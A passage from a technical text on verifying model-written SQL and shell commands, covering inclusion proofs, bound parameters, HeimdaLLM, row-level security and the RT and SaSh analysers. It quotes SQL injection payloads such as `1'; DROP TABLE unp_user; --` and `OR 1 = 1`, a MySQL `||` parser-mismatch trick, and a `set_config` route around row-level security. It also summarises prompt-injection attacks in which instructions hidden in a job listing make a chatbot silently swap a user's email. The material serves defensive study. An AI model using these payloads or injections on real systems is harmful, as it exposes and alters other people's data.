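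For personal names, a developer might choose `[A-Za-z][A-Za-z' -]*`, which requires a letter and then allows letters, apostrophes, spaces and hyphens. Its accepting state is "name". The search goes from (start, clean) to (name, clean) on the letter `A`, and then to (name, broken) on an apostrophe. Both automata accept in that pair, so the inclusion fails. If the search tries shorter strings first, it finds a shortest witness, here `A'`. No single character would work, because the pattern requires the first one to be a letter.

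A witness shows that the pattern allows a value outside *S*, but that value may not work as an attack. Putting `A'` into the bookshop's query gives `author = 'A'';`. The database treats the two quotation marks after `A` as one apostrophe, so the string never ends and the database rejects the query. A developer still has to check whether an attacker could exploit what the pattern allows. In this case an attacker could, because the attack at the start of this section, `A' OR 'a' LIKE 'a`, contains only letters, apostrophes and spaces and so matches the pattern for names.

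### Escaping the value or binding it

The application can *escape* the value by doubling each apostrophe before it builds the query. If it also keeps backslashes out, as the name pattern does, the value cannot end its string early, and the database searches for the attack text as an author's name. Banning apostrophes would also fix the proof, but it would reject names like O'Brian.

The inclusion test can confirm this repair. After escaping, a name matches `[A-Za-z]([A-Za-z -]|'')*`, in which apostrophes occur only in pairs. The safe set can now include paired apostrophes, so its automaton needs one more state, "half", which it enters after the first apostrophe of a pair. A second apostrophe takes it back to "clean", and anything else takes it to "broken". The complement accepts any string that ends in "half" or "broken". An escaped name never reaches "broken", and it reaches "half" only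 partway through a pair, where the pattern does not accept, so no counterexample remains.

Escaping protects a value only if the developer has put quotation marks around it. Su and Wassermann give the example of an online shop that escapes a card type by doubling its apostrophes, then inserts it without quotation marks into a query that compares it with a column of numbers. The input `2 OR 1=1` contains no apostrophe, so escaping leaves it unchanged, and the shop displays every stored card number. In that position, the safe values are numbers, such as those matching `[0-9]+`. Whether a value is safe therefore depends on the query and on where the value appears in it.

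For ordinary values there is a better repair. With a *bound parameter*, the application passes the query and the value separately:

```python
db.execute("SELECT title, price FROM books WHERE author = %s", [name])
```

The `%s` marks where the value belongs. Usually, the database parses the query with this gap in it and receives the value afterwards, so the value cannot change the parse tree. The developer then doesn't need escaping, a safe set or an inclusion proof for that position, and a name containing an apostrophe, such as O'Brian, works as a value. Some database libraries instead insert an escaped copy of the value themselves, in which case their escaping code is part of the trusted base.

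The method works only if the model's text stays out of the query itself. Srinivasan and Bleaney's *PEP 675* introduced a Python type called `LiteralString` for text written in the program's own code. As LWN explains, a database library can require this type for the query and accept ordinary strings as parameters. If a developer pastes a user's identifier into the query, a type checker reports the error before the program runs.

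A bound parameter can supply only a value. It cannot supply a table or column name, a sort direction or an operator, because the database needs these to build the tree. If the model chooses the sort column, the application has to put that column's name into the query as text. A pattern such as `[a-z_]+` prevents the name from adding other code to the query, but it would also allow columns that customers should not be able to use. A fixed list such as `title|price` is better, and is also a small regular language.

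Binding a value does not check what it means. In a search with `LIKE`, the character `%` matches any text, so a customer who supplies `%` as the author gets every book without any SQL injection.

### From the constraint to the sink

Where the application does put the model's text into a query, the complete argument has three steps:

1. The value *v* is in *T*, because constrained decoding allows nothing else or a check at use has tested it.
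2. *T* ⊆ *S*, which the developer proves once.
3. Therefore *v* is in *S* and cannot change the structure of the query.

The proof that *T* ⊆ *S* does not depend on the model, but the developer has to repeat it when someone edits the pattern or the query.

Restricting the value to *T* is essential. Ray and Ligatti prove, for a simplified version of SQL, that every application that always copies some untrusted input unchanged into its query is open to injection. The bookshop's original code does this. Their proof doesn't cover an application that refuses every value outside *T*, because such an application doesn't copy everything it receives.

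In older web applications, *T* isn't written down, so Wassermann and Su (2007), in *Sound and Precise Analysis of Web Applications for Injection Vulnerabilities*, compute it from the program. Their tool follows each string through the code, builds a grammar for all the queries the program could send, and marks the parts that a user can influence. On five web applications, it found 19 real vulnerabilities involving text directly from users and raised 5 false alarms. For the largest application, with about 130,000 lines, working out the possible strings took more than three and a half hours. A tool call with a declared pattern avoids most of this work because the value arrives in its own field and *T* is already known.

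The pattern must be the one that the code really applies. One of the vulnerabilities was in a news system that tested a user number with the pattern `[0-9]+`. The programmer had left out the anchors `^` and `$`, which tie a pattern to the beginning and end of the text, so the test passed any text with a digit somewhere in it. It accepted this:

```
1'; DROP TABLE unp_user; --
```

An inclusion proof for `[0-9]+` would succeed but would not apply to that program, because its real *T* is every string that contains a digit. JSON Schema patterns can also match anywhere in a string, which is why the refund tool's pattern for order numbers has both anchors.

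The inclusion proof can also rest on the wrong safe set. If the developer follows the SQL standard and allows backslashes in *S*, but the database treats them as escape characters, as MySQL does by default, the proof is still valid but doesn't show that the value is safe in that database.

Even when both steps hold, other code may change the value before it reaches the sink. For example, the text `%27` is in *S*, but a later function that decodes web addresses will turn it into an apostrophe. JSON can also represent an apostrophe as `\u0027`, so the application should test the value after parsing the call. Neither kind of decoding changes hostnames that match the pattern above, because they contain no `%` or backslash.

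Shortening a value can be just as harmful. If the code cuts an escaped name to 20 characters and the cut falls between two paired apostrophes, the remaining apostrophe pairs with the closing quotation mark. The original set *S* does not have this problem, because shortening a string that has no quotation marks or backslashes cannot introduce any.

Finally, the application may reuse the value elsewhere. The hostname pattern also matches `-rf`, which is safe between quotation marks in a query, but many shell commands would interpret it as an option. The USENIX magazine ;login: (2018) describes a class of "forwarding flaws", in which one component passes malicious input to another that parses it correctly but not as anyone intended. The application can also read a value back from the database and put it into a new query. Wassermann and Su found code that read a user's number and name from stored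 data, tested the number, and put the name into the next query without testing it.

### Types that describe strings

Errors of this kind are easy to make because most programming languages give all strings the same type, whether they hold a hostname, a web page or half a query. *FLAT* (Zhu and Zeller, 2025) proposes using formal languages as types, so that a function can require a web address and reject anything else. A type in FLAT is a context-free grammar, with a condition written in ordinary code where the grammar is not enough.

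The hostname query above comes from the project's code page, flatypes' *FLAT-PY*, which describes the implementation for Python. In the example, one function extracts the hostname from a web address by taking the text between `://` and the next slash, and another puts the result into the query. An attacker can supply this address:

```
https://localhost'); DROP TABLE users --/
```

Without types, the extracted "hostname" ends the string in the query and adds a command that deletes a table. If the developer declares that the function takes a `URL` and returns a `Host`, FLAT-PY adds runtime checks for these types to the program, and the malicious address causes an error when it is passed to the function.

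FLAT-PY can also fuzz a function, which means running it on random strings generated from a grammar. In the example, fuzzing reveals that the function drops the last character of the hostname when no slash follows it, so `https://example.com` yields `example.co`. The type `Host` cannot catch this bug because `example.co` is a valid hostname and safe in the query, even though it is the wrong one. To catch it, a developer can add a condition that the result must equal the hostname in the address's parse tree.

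The published version, *FLAT* (2026), reports case studies on fragments of real Python code, in which random inputs revealed logical bugs and the developer had to add a reasonable number of annotations. In the three case studies in Zhu and Zeller's preprint, the checks made the programs much slower, which is tolerable in testing, FLAT-PY's intended use. The studies show that the types help to find bugs in small pieces of code, but they don't measure how well the types would protect a running service. In the three-step argument, FLAT-PY's run-time checks establish that a value is in *T*, but somebody still has to prove that every `Host` is safe between the quotation marks.

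*Statically Typed String Sanitation Inside a Python* (Fulton, Omar and Aldrich, 2014) describes an earlier system meant to provide that proof. Its types are regular languages, with rules for what happens when a program joins strings or replaces parts of them. A type checker can then verify, before the program runs, that the program cleans a value properly, so no redundant test is needed later. Li and colleagues apply the same kind of inclusion check between the stages of a shell pipeline.

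*Executable Refinement Types* (Knowles, 2014) describes SAGE, an experimental language that combines the two approaches. Its refinement types attach a condition to an ordinary type, and the condition can be any test written in the language. One example defines `Credential` as a string of letters and digits, and requires this type for the user name and password in a login query. When a program passes ordinary strings to the login function, SAGE tries to prove that every string is a `Credential`. It can neither prove nor refute this, so it inserts a run-time test. If a user then enters `admin --`, the test fails and SAGE stores the string as a counterexample. The next time someone compiles the program, SAGE rejects it.

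The login query in this example has no quotation marks around the two values, which is probably an oversight, but an instructive one. With the user name `name` and the password `pwd`, both perfectly valid credentials, the condition becomes:

```sql
WHERE name =name and pwd=pwd
```

The database now compares each column with itself, and the login succeeds if any customer in the table has both fields filled in. The type blocks the attack that Knowles describes, but its values are safe only between quotation marks. *SafeStrings* (2019) likewise treats a typed string as a certificate that somebody has checked the content, so other code doesn't need to check it again. Such a certificate is useful only if it specifies which kind of sink the content is safe for.

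### When inclusion can be decided

SAGE could not settle its question because its conditions can be arbitrary programs. With patterns and grammars, the answer depends on which kind of language describes each set:

| Permitted values *T* | Safe set *S* | Can an algorithm always decide *T* ⊆ *S*? |
|---|---|---|
| regular | regular | yes |
| context-free | regular | yes |
| regular | context-free | no |
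| context-free | context-free | no |

The product construction above always finishes for two regular languages, since there are finitely many pairs of states. It can be slow for some patterns, because an automaton with exactly one next state for every character may need exponentially more states than the pattern has symbols. The automaton for the safe set of quoted values needs two states.

The method still works if *T* is context-free, for example because the value is a nested formula. For each symbol *X* of the grammar and each pair of states *i* and *j* of the complement automaton, the algorithm creates a new symbol *X<sub>ij</sub>* for the strings that *X* can generate and that take the automaton from *i* to *j*. It then checks whether the grammar's start symbol can generate a string that takes the automaton from "clean" to "broken". The earlier grammar for bracketed numbers generates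 only digits and brackets. These characters keep the automaton in "clean", so every bracketed number is safe between the quotation marks. Wassermann and Su use this construction and carry the marks for user-supplied text over to the new symbols.

The method fails when *S* is context-free, because the complement of a context-free language need not be context-free, so the algorithm may have no grammar in which to look for a counterexample. No algorithm can solve the general problem. If *T* is the set of all strings, which is regular, then *T* ⊆ *S* means that the grammar for *S* generates every string, and no algorithm can decide this for every context-free grammar. But if a parser can read the safe language from left to right with a stack and never has to guess, the complement has the same property, and an algorithm can decide whether the safe language contains a given regular language.

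The difficulty arises when the model supplies more than a quoted value. If it writes a whole condition, with brackets nested to any depth, the safe set is part of the SQL grammar. Here Wassermann and Su test whether they can map each symbol of the program's grammar to a symbol of the SQL grammar so that every rule still holds. Such a mapping proves the inclusion, but the inclusion may be true even when they find no mapping, and their tool then reports a possible vulnerability. Checking each string at use avoids the problem, because it is always decidable whether a context-free grammar generates a given string.

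## A whole database query written by the model

The bookshop's search always has the same form, so a developer can write the query in advance and bind the value. Open-ended questions need a different query each time. Suppose a film-rental service lets customers ask about their own accounts, and one of them types "how much have i spent renting movies, broken down by month?" The application describes the tables to the model, and the model writes the whole query:

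```sql
SELECT
  SUM(payment.amount) AS spent,
  strftime('%Y-%m', payment.payment_date) AS month
FROM customer
JOIN payment ON customer.customer_id = payment.customer_id
JOIN rental ON payment.rental_id = rental.rental_id
WHERE customer.customer_id = :customer_id
GROUP BY month
```

Each `JOIN` combines matching rows from two tables, so every payment appears with its rental and its customer. The query then adds up the payments for each month.

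The example follows one in the documentation of HeimdaLLM, a Python library from 2023 that checks model-written queries before the database runs them. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis et al., 2025) credits HeimdaLLM with pioneering this kind of check. Bound parameters cannot replace the check, because they protect a query structure that the developer has fixed, and here the model chooses the structure. The earlier definition of injection does not apply either, because there is no developer's query to compare with the model's.

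The application still binds one value, `:customer_id`, to the logged-in customer's number when it runs the query, so the model can refer to the current customer but cannot choose who that is. The checker has to make sure the query restricts its results to that customer.

### From text to a checked tree

HeimdaLLM parses the query with a grammar that covers only part of SQL. The grammar describes `SELECT`, the statement that reads data, and no statement that changes data, so `DROP TABLE` is simply a syntax error. HeimdaLLM then walks the resulting tree and compares its parts with rules that the developer has written. HeimdaLLM's *Validation only*, a quickstart guide, sets these rules for the film-rental service:

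| Part of the query | Rule |
|---|---|
| columns | any named column, but not `*`, which selects all of them |
| joins | payments to rentals by rental number, and customers to payments by customer number |
| functions | only those on a default list, which includes `strftime` and `SUM` |
| current user | a condition must equate `customer.customer_id` with `:customer_id` |
| rows | at most 10 |

The list of functions keeps out calls such as `pg_sleep`, which can occupy a PostgreSQL database for days, and stored functions that change data when a query calls them. The column rule is so loose that if the customer table contained a password hash, a query could return the current customer's hash.

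The film-rental query breaks only the last rule, because it has no row limit. HeimdaLLM fixes this by adding `LIMIT 10` to the tree. It makes such repairs in a first pass and applies the rules strictly in a second. According to HeimdaLLM's *SQL Reconstruction*, it can also lower a limit that is too high, remove forbidden columns from the results, and add a table name to a column that lacks one.

Repairing a query by adding a ten-row limit can change the answer. A customer who has rented films in 14 different months would get only ten of those months, in no guaranteed order, and the model might present them as the full history. The database may also still have to add up millions of payments, because the limit applies only to the rows returned.

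One repair in the documentation would break the query. The original query gives the table `users` the alias `u`, but the repaired version refers to `users.id`. PostgreSQL rejects this because the alias replaces the table's name within the query. The mistake exposes no data, but the user gets an error instead of an answer.

### A condition that every row must meet

Without its `WHERE` line, the film-rental query is still valid SQL and uses only permitted columns, joins and functions, but it would return the monthly takings from all customers. HeimdaLLM rejects it because it has no condition on the current user. Replacing `:customer_id` with a specific customer number also breaks the rule, since the model would then determine whose payments are shown.

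The condition can also be present and have no effect:

```sql
WHERE customer.customer_id = :customer_id
  AND payment.amount > 0
  OR 1 = 1
```

SQL applies `AND` before `OR`, so the conditions form this tree:

```
OR
├─ AND
│  ├─ customer.customer_id = :customer_id
│  └─ payment.amount > 0
└─ 1 = 1
```

A row qualifies if either branch is true, and `1 = 1` is true for every row, so the query again covers everyone's payments. A checker that only searched the text for the required condition would find it and pass the query. The checker must instead establish that the database cannot use a row unless the condition holds for that row, which means that the whole `WHERE` clause must imply the condition.

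HeimdaLLM approximates this by looking at the condition's position, as HeimdaLLM's *SQL* explains. The checker starts at the top of the tree and works down. If `OR` connects the conditions at some level, the checker ignores everything at that level and below. The required condition therefore counts only if `AND` connects it, and every branch that contains it, to the rest of the clause. In the tree above, the search ends at the root and the checker should reject the query. The same rule catches an `OR` inside several layers of brackets, which a person could easily miss.

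This test is stricter than a check for implication. If *C* is the required condition, a query for "(*C* and more than 5 dollars) or (*C* and less than 1 dollar)" returns only the customer's own payments, but the test rejects it because its top-level operator is `OR`. The model can rewrite it as "*C* and (more than 5 dollars or less than 1 dollar)", which passes.

The published rule mentions only `AND` and `OR`, but a checker also has to handle `NOT`. The clause `NOT (C AND payment.amount > 1000)` has *C* under an `AND`, yet the whole clause is true for every payment by another customer.

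A mandatory condition restricts only the customer table, so the payments are restricted too only if the query joins the tables correctly. If both tables recorded a shop number and the query joined them on it, the query would return the payments of everyone who used the current customer's shop. The developer therefore lists the permitted joins. HeimdaLLM's grammar also excludes outer joins, which keep rows that have no match. If the user condition is part of an outer join, other people's payments can appear in the results even though they don't match.

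A query can also reveal a column's contents without displaying them. A query with the condition `secret LIKE 'a%'` returns a row only if the secret begins with "a", and further queries can find the remaining letters. By default, HeimdaLLM therefore forbids a query from using a column in conditions, groupings or sort orders if the query is not allowed to select that column.

Sometimes the checker rejects a correct query because the model has put the user condition in an unexpected place, such as inside a join, where it applies to `rental.customer_id`. HeimdaLLM's *Constraint Validator* tells developers to list each column that can identify the user, and a query has to restrict at least one of them.

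The project appears to be dormant. In May 2025, Ecosyste.ms, an index of open-source software, listed the last change to the code as July 2024, although the owner had not archived the repository. In HeimdaLLM's *FAQ*, the author is still organising an independent security audit and advises against production use without a careful risk assessment until the audit is complete. HeimdaLLM is therefore more useful as an example of the technique than as a component to install.

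### When two parsers disagree

The checker tests the tree that its own grammar produces, but the database parses the text again. If the two parsers disagree, the checker can approve one query while the database runs another. For example, the symbol `||` joins two pieces of text in standard SQL, but in MySQL, with its usual settings, it means `OR`:

```sql
WHERE customer.customer_id = :customer_id
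  AND payment.amount > 0 || 1
```

A checker that follows the standard parses this as a comparison between the amount and the text `01`, joined to the user condition by `AND`, and passes the query. MySQL treats the `||` as `OR` and applies it last, so the query returns every row, because `1` is always true. Backslashes can cause the same kind of mismatch, because only some databases treat them as escape characters. So can comments that begin with `/*!`, because MySQL runs their contents while other parsers skip them.

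HeimdaLLM's *Safely executing LLM-generated SQL* acknowledges that each database has its own quirks and that determined attackers may find holes in the grammar. HeimdaLLM reduces the risk with separate grammars for SQLite, MySQL and PostgreSQL. A small grammar also helps, since it can leave out any construct whose meaning varies between databases.

A checker can avoid most of the problem by using the database's own parser, as the shell verifier in *Look Before You Leap* does for commands. It can also discard the model's text after the check and print a new query from the approved tree, with brackets around every operation. The last condition then becomes `(payment.amount > (0 || 1))`. MySQL still interprets `||` as `OR`, but only inside the brackets, so the user condition remains mandatory.

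### Controls inside the database

The database can also enforce the rules itself. It applies them to its own parse of the query, so no second parser is involved.

The simplest control is a *role*, a named set of permissions that the database attaches to a connection. *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Carreira and colleagues, 2023) suggests giving the application two connections, one with a read-only role for the chatbot and one with full permissions for everything else. The database then rejects any query from the chatbot that would change data. A read-only role is safer than a read-only transaction, which the application opens before running the query. If the database accepts several statements in one string, the model's text could close the transaction and then change data.

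A role can exclude whole tables and, in some databases, columns. It cannot separate one customer's payments from another's if they are in the same table. *Row-level security* can, by attaching a condition to the table itself. In PostgreSQL, after switching the feature on for the table, a developer could write:

```sql
CREATE POLICY own_payments ON payment
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::int);
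```

The application stores the customer's number in `app.customer_id` before it runs the model's query. A row-level security policy in PostgreSQL then limits the query to that customer's payments, so adding `OR 1 = 1` to the query does not expose anyone else's. Each table with personal data needs its own policy, and developers have to update the policies when the tables change.

A *view* is a stored query that other queries can use like a table. The developer can define a view that contains only the current customer's payments and let the chatbot's role read the view but not the table. This also works in MySQL, which has no built-in row-level security. Pedro and colleagues' query rewriting does something similar from outside the database. If user 5 asks for everyone's email addresses, their program turns the model's query into this one:

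```sql
SELECT email FROM (
  SELECT * FROM users WHERE user_id = 5
) AS users_alias
```

The inner query selects the user's own row, so any `OR` that the model writes can apply only to that row. The program does not need to work out whether a condition is mandatory, but it must find every mention of the table, so it again depends on a parser.

Database controls fail if someone configures them badly. PostgreSQL exempts superusers from row-level security, and the sample chatbot in the paper by Pedro and colleagues connects as `postgres`, which is usually a superuser. The variable `app.customer_id` is another weak point, because a `SELECT` can call PostgreSQL's `set_config` function to change it to another customer's number. A list of permitted functions would prevent this, as would a separate database account for each customer, with a policy that depends on the account instead of the variable.

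| Control | Prevents changes to data | Hides other customers' rows |
|---|---|---|
| read-only role | yes | no |
| row-level security | not by itself | yes |
| view, with no access to the table | with a read-only role | yes |
| separate copy of the data for each customer | changes affect only the copy | yes |
| tree check | if the parsers agree | if the parsers agree |

HeimdaLLM's comparison of these methods recommends tree checks and separate copies, and advises against the others because none of them solves the whole problem. However, it considers each control on its own, and a connection can combine a read-only role, which stops someone deleting a table, with row-level security, which hides rows. Together, these two controls are a better basis for the guarantee than a tree check, which can then restrict functions and reject bad queries early. SQLite, the database in the film-rental example,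 has neither accounts nor row-level security, so the closest equivalent there is a separate file for each customer.

When the database blocks a query, the customer still has no answer. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (2026) argues that the database should enforce the permissions, but that the model should also take them into account, so that it writes a permitted query or properly refuses. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (2025) tests two ways to do this. In one, a single model receives the user's permissions and either writes the query or answers "Access Denied". In the other, a second model checks the finished query against the permissions. *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (2026) uses constrained decoding to apply the policy while the model writes the query. Its policy depends on how a query uses a column, so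 it could allow salaries in an average but not in a list.

### Attacks through the prompt

In August 2023, Pedro and colleagues studied how an outsider can make a chatbot write harmful SQL. They built a job-listing site with LangChain, a library that connects models to other software, and gave the chatbot full access to the database. With LangChain's default prompt, a user could delete a table or list its contents just by asking.

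The next test added rules to the prompt, including one to return only the current user's data. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, GPT-3.5 wrote a query with the condition `user_id = 2 AND user_id = 1`, which no row can satisfy. But when the attacker claimed to be user 2, the model dropped the restriction. The claim would have had no effect if the query had used a placeholder for the user ID that the application fills in from the login.

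Other attacks came through the data. In one, the attacker hid instructions in a job description. When the victim asked about available jobs, the chatbot read the description, replaced the victim's email address with the attacker's, and answered the question without mentioning the change.

The researchers ran each of seven attacks 30 times on GPT-3.5. Every attack succeeded every time, except one that worked in 60% of runs on a version of the chatbot that could make several queries per question. They also tried the attacks on six other models. All the models that could run the chatbot reliably were vulnerable, although the attack that changed an email address failed or left traces on some of them. GPT-4 was the hardest to manipulate.

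These models are now old, so the success rates are weak evidence about current ones. Newer evidence of this kind seems scarce. In August 2026, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian still used this study as their documented case of SQL injection through a model, and their own experiments tested a different attack.

The results for the defences are more durable because permissions and query rewriting do not depend on the model. Pedro and colleagues tested the defences on a bookshop application with about two million reviews. Restricting permissions stopped the attacks that changed data. Rewriting queries stopped the attacks that read other users' data and added an average of 1.87 milliseconds per query. A second model, which inspected query results for hidden instructions, took about 0.4 seconds and was itself open to prompt injection.

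In one attack, a job description contained an instruction to answer that there were no jobs. Neither permissions nor query rewriting stopped it. The model's query was `SELECT "description" FROM job_postings`, which the user's question required. The false answer came from the text the query returned, so no check on the query could have prevented it.

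## Shell commands checked before they run

A shell rewrites a command line before running it, whereas a database parses a query and then runs it. The rewritten command depends on variables, files and the output of other commands, so a check that examines only the model's text may examine a different command from the one that runs.

### How a command line changes before it runs

This rewriting is known as *expansion*. Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues, in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*, list seven kinds. The examples below are for a user named `ana` who has set the variable `dir` to `old reports`:

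| Expansion | Written | Result |
|---|---|---|
| tilde | `~/notes` | `/home/ana/notes` |
| parameter | `$USER` | `ana` |
| command substitution | `$(uname)` | `Linux`, the output of the command `uname` |
| arithmetic | `$((2+3))` | `5` |
| field splitting | `$dir` | two arguments, `old` and `reports` |
| pathname | `*.txt` | the name of every matching file |
| quote removal | `"$dir"` | one argument, `old reports` |

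Quotation marks can change what a command deletes. If the variable `dir` contains `old reports`, `rm -r "$dir"` deletes the folder with that name, while `rm -r $dir` deletes two other folders, `old` and `reports`. The shell doesn't expand variables inside single quotation marks, so `rm -r '$dir'` tries to delete a folder named `$dir`.

A command line can also contain a program for another interpreter. In `ssh backup "ls $HOME"`, the local shell replaces `$HOME` with the path of the local home folder, and a second shell on the machine `backup` runs the result. With single quotation marks, the second shell replaces `$HOME` instead, so the command may list a different folder.

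Even after the shell expands a command, the command's effect depends on its options and on which files exist. `mv report.txt archive` moves `report.txt` into `archive` if that is a folder, overwrites `archive` if it is a file, and renames `report.txt` to `archive` if nothing with that name exists.

An application can avoid most of these problems if the model supplies only a value:

```python
subprocess.run(["cat", "--", path])
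```

This starts `cat` without a shell, so `cat` receives `path` as exactly one argument, much like a bound parameter in a query. The `--` marks the end of the options, so `cat` doesn't treat a value such as `-rf` as an option. When the model writes the whole command line, the application needs some other check.

### A type for each command

Li and colleagues presented RT at OSDI, a conference on operating systems, in July 2026. RT gives each command a type with two halves, both of them regular languages. One describes the lines that the command accepts and the other the lines that it produces. These are the types for the pipeline that searches for book files:

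| Command | Accepts | Produces |
|---|---|---|
| `find .` | no input | `\.(/.+)?` |
| `grep -E 'book[0-9]+\.txt'` | `.*` | the input lines that match `.*book[0-9]+\.txt.*` |
| `xargs cat` | `[^ \t]+` or `".+"` or `'.+'` | `.*` |

RT works from left to right. `find .` produces either a single dot or `./` followed by at least one more character. `grep` accepts any line, so RT finds no problem between these two commands. It then intersects the output of `find` with the pattern that `grep` searches for, which gives the type of the lines that leave `grep`:

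```
\./.*book[0-9]+\.txt.*
```

`xargs cat` accepts a line only if it contains no spaces or tabs or is entirely enclosed in quotation marks. RT therefore has to check whether every line that `grep` can produce meets this condition, which is the same inclusion test as for the hostname in the database query. The test fails on `./ book0.txt`, the witness given earlier, which matches the type above because `.*` can match the space, but is not enclosed in quotation marks. ShellCheck, a widely used tool that searches scripts for suspicious patterns, gives no warning about this script.

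Li and colleagues repair the script with a stricter pattern, `^\./book[0-9]+\.txt$`. The inclusion now holds because no matching line contains a space. But the script is meant to search the whole tree, and the new pattern excludes every file in a subfolder. The types describe only what each line looks like, so they cannot show that lines are missing.

The entry for `xargs cat` is also slightly wrong. RT accepts the filename `./o'brien-book1.txt` because it matches `[^ \t]+`, but `xargs` treats the apostrophe as an opening quote and stops with an error when it finds no closing quote.

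The rest of the script splits the books into words, changes them to capitals, keeps those that occur in a dictionary file and counts them:

```sh
tr -cs A-Za-z '\n' | tr '[:lower:]' '[:upper:]' |
  grep -fw dict.txt | sort | uniq -c | sort -rn
```

If the dictionary is in lower case, no capitalised word can match, and the script prints nothing. RT cannot detect this from the script alone, but it has an optional mode that reads `dict.txt`, builds a type from its words and finds that that type's intersection with `[A-Z]*` is empty. This result holds only for the file's current contents.

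Li and colleagues report that RT gives no warnings once both errors are corrected, but the script still has a third error. The option `-f` takes the text directly after it as a file name, so `grep -fw dict.txt` reads its patterns from a file called `w` and searches for them in `dict.txt`. The writer probably meant `-wf dict.txt`. RT's database has to parse options as the real command does, but it evidently fails to do so here.

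### Commands that RT does not know

RT's database covers 71 of the 106 GNU coreutils, the basic commands of most Linux systems, and 86% of the commands in the evaluation scripts from GitHub. RT assigns any other command the type `.* → .*`, which accepts any line and may produce any line. Li and colleagues call this default "trivially correct for all command invocations".

It does not meet their own definition of a sound command type, which has two conditions:

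- The input half contains only lines that are guaranteed not to make the command crash or misbehave.
- The output half contains every line that the command could produce.

The default meets the condition on output, because `.*` matches every line. It meets the condition on input only if the command can safely handle any line, and RT has no information about that for a command missing from its database. If the database had no entry for `xargs cat`, RT would accept file names with spaces as input, and the faulty pipeline would pass the check.

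An input type that contains no lines would be sound for every command, but RT would then reject almost any pipeline that sends data to an unknown command. The permissive default is reasonable for a tool that looks for bugs. If an application uses RT to decide whether a model's command may run, it should treat an unknown command as unchecked.

The default can also cause false alarms later in the pipeline. `sort -n` expects each line to begin with a number, but when it follows a command whose output type is `.*`, RT cannot rule out lines that don't.

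*From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again* (Lazarek, Jung and colleagues, 2025) proposes two ways to deal with unknown commands. One is to have a language model draft a command's specification from its manual, then test the draft by running the command in many prepared environments. The other is a monitor that checks the lines entering and leaving the command while it runs. The monitor can stop a bad line before the next command receives it, but earlier commands may already have made changes by then.

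### How many faults RT finds

Li and colleagues tested RT on 954 programs, of which 730 were correct and 224 faulty. RT classified 864 of them correctly (91%), taking 0.02 seconds per program on average and never more than a second. A checker that never gave a warning would have scored 77%, so the separate counts are more informative:

| Version of RT | False alarms, of 730 correct programs | Faults found, of 224 |
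|---|---|---|
| full | 27 | 161 |
| without transducers | 147 | 176 |
| without heuristics | 16 | 94 |

A *transducer* is a finite automaton that also writes output as it reads. The transducer for `tr a-z A-Z` writes `A` when it reads `a`, and likewise for the other letters, so RT can calculate that an input of type `[a-z]+` becomes `[A-Z]+`. Transducers reduced the false-positive rate from 20% to 4%. They also reduced the number of faults found, probably because some of the vaguer types had triggered warnings about faulty programs for the wrong reason. But when developers added comments stating what the data should look like, RT found more faults with transducers (210) than without them (200).

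Transducers cannot describe every command exactly. For example, `sed -E 's/(.*)/\1\1/'` writes each line twice, and if the input can be any string, the set of doubled strings is not regular. RT then has to use a larger set.

The *heuristics* are rules that flag pipelines that violate no type but are probably mistakes, such as one that sorts numbers alphabetically or one that can never produce output. Without them, RT found only 42% of the faults, so the inclusion test accounts for only part of the 91%.

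RT missed 63 faults. Of these, 49 were in programs whose output had the wrong format, and RT had no specification of the correct format. The other 14 involved properties that the types cannot express. For example, `uniq` removes repeated lines only if they are adjacent, and a type for single lines doesn't describe the order of the lines.

RT was built for developers' scripts, not for commands that language models write. Its evaluation used a model only to write 120 of the 224 faulty test programs, with instructions to make common mistakes. Deliberate mistakes may differ from those a model makes while trying to complete a task, so the results are weak evidence of how well RT would work in an agent.

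RT also doesn't check what a command does to files. A pipeline that passes well-formed file names to `rm` has no type error, even if the user wanted to keep the files.

### Following changes to files

SaSh, the system that Lazarek and colleagues built, is meant to find such effects before a script runs. It uses *symbolic execution*, which means that it works through the script with symbols in place of unknown values and records what must be true of them. For each command it has a short specification of what the command needs and what it changes. Here are two of them, slightly simplified:

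| Command | Needs | After success |
|---|---|---|
| `cat p` | `p` is a file | `p` is a file that something has read |
| `rm -r p` | `p` is a folder, or a file that something has read | `p` no longer exists |

In the script `rm -r notes; cat notes`, the first command removes `notes` and the second needs it to be a file. No initial state of the disk allows both commands to succeed, so SaSh warns that `cat` will fail. It also detects possible data loss by checking whether a file has been read before the script deletes it, because deleting an unread file may destroy the only copy.

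The best-known example in the paper is a bug in the Linux updater for Steam, a games platform, which deleted users' files in 2015. These are the two lines that caused it:

```sh
STEAMROOT="$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"
rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*
```

`$0` is the path used to start the script, and `${0%/*}` removes the last slash and everything after it. For `/opt/steam/update.sh`, this leaves `/opt/steam`. The script enters that folder, stores its path in `STEAMROOT` and later deletes its contents. But if someone starts the script as `sh update.sh`, there is no slash to remove. `cd` then tries to enter a file and fails, `echo` never runs, and `STEAMROOT` is empty. The last line becomes `rm -rf /*`, which deletes everything the user has permission to delete.

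SaSh follows both outcomes of `cd`. If `cd` succeeds, `STEAMROOT` is the name of a folder. If it fails, `STEAMROOT` is empty and the script deletes the contents of the root folder, so SaSh gives a warning. In the full updater, 342 lines separate `cd` from the delete command. SaSh found the bug in 4.8 seconds.

SaSh decides whether to warn by using an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values make a logical formula true. Let *P* be everything that holds on one path through the script, and let *N* be the condition that the script deletes no critical folder. SaSh warns if *P* ∧ *N* is impossible, meaning the script is certain to delete a critical folder on that path. A sound check would warn whenever *P* ∧ ¬*N* is possible, meaning the script could delete one. Lazarek and colleagues chose the weaker test because almost any script containing `rm` is dangerous in some environment.

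Their repaired version of the updater shows what the weaker test can miss. It deletes files only if `STEAMROOT` is not empty. If the script is in the root folder and someone starts it there as `./update.sh`, `STEAMROOT` is `/` and the script still deletes everything, although they describe it as safe in every environment. SaSh doesn't warn about this version, because most other values of `STEAMROOT` are harmless. In 2025, Lazarek and colleagues had used a stronger condition, which compares the folder with `/` and prevents the deletion.

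SaSh found 115 of the 116 documented bugs in 61 real scripts within a minute, including 97 within a second. It gave no warnings about these bugs after they were fixed. ShellCheck gave a relevant warning for 42 of the bugs. The bug SaSh missed was in a Debian installation script that deletes a folder chosen by the user, which is often what a user wants.

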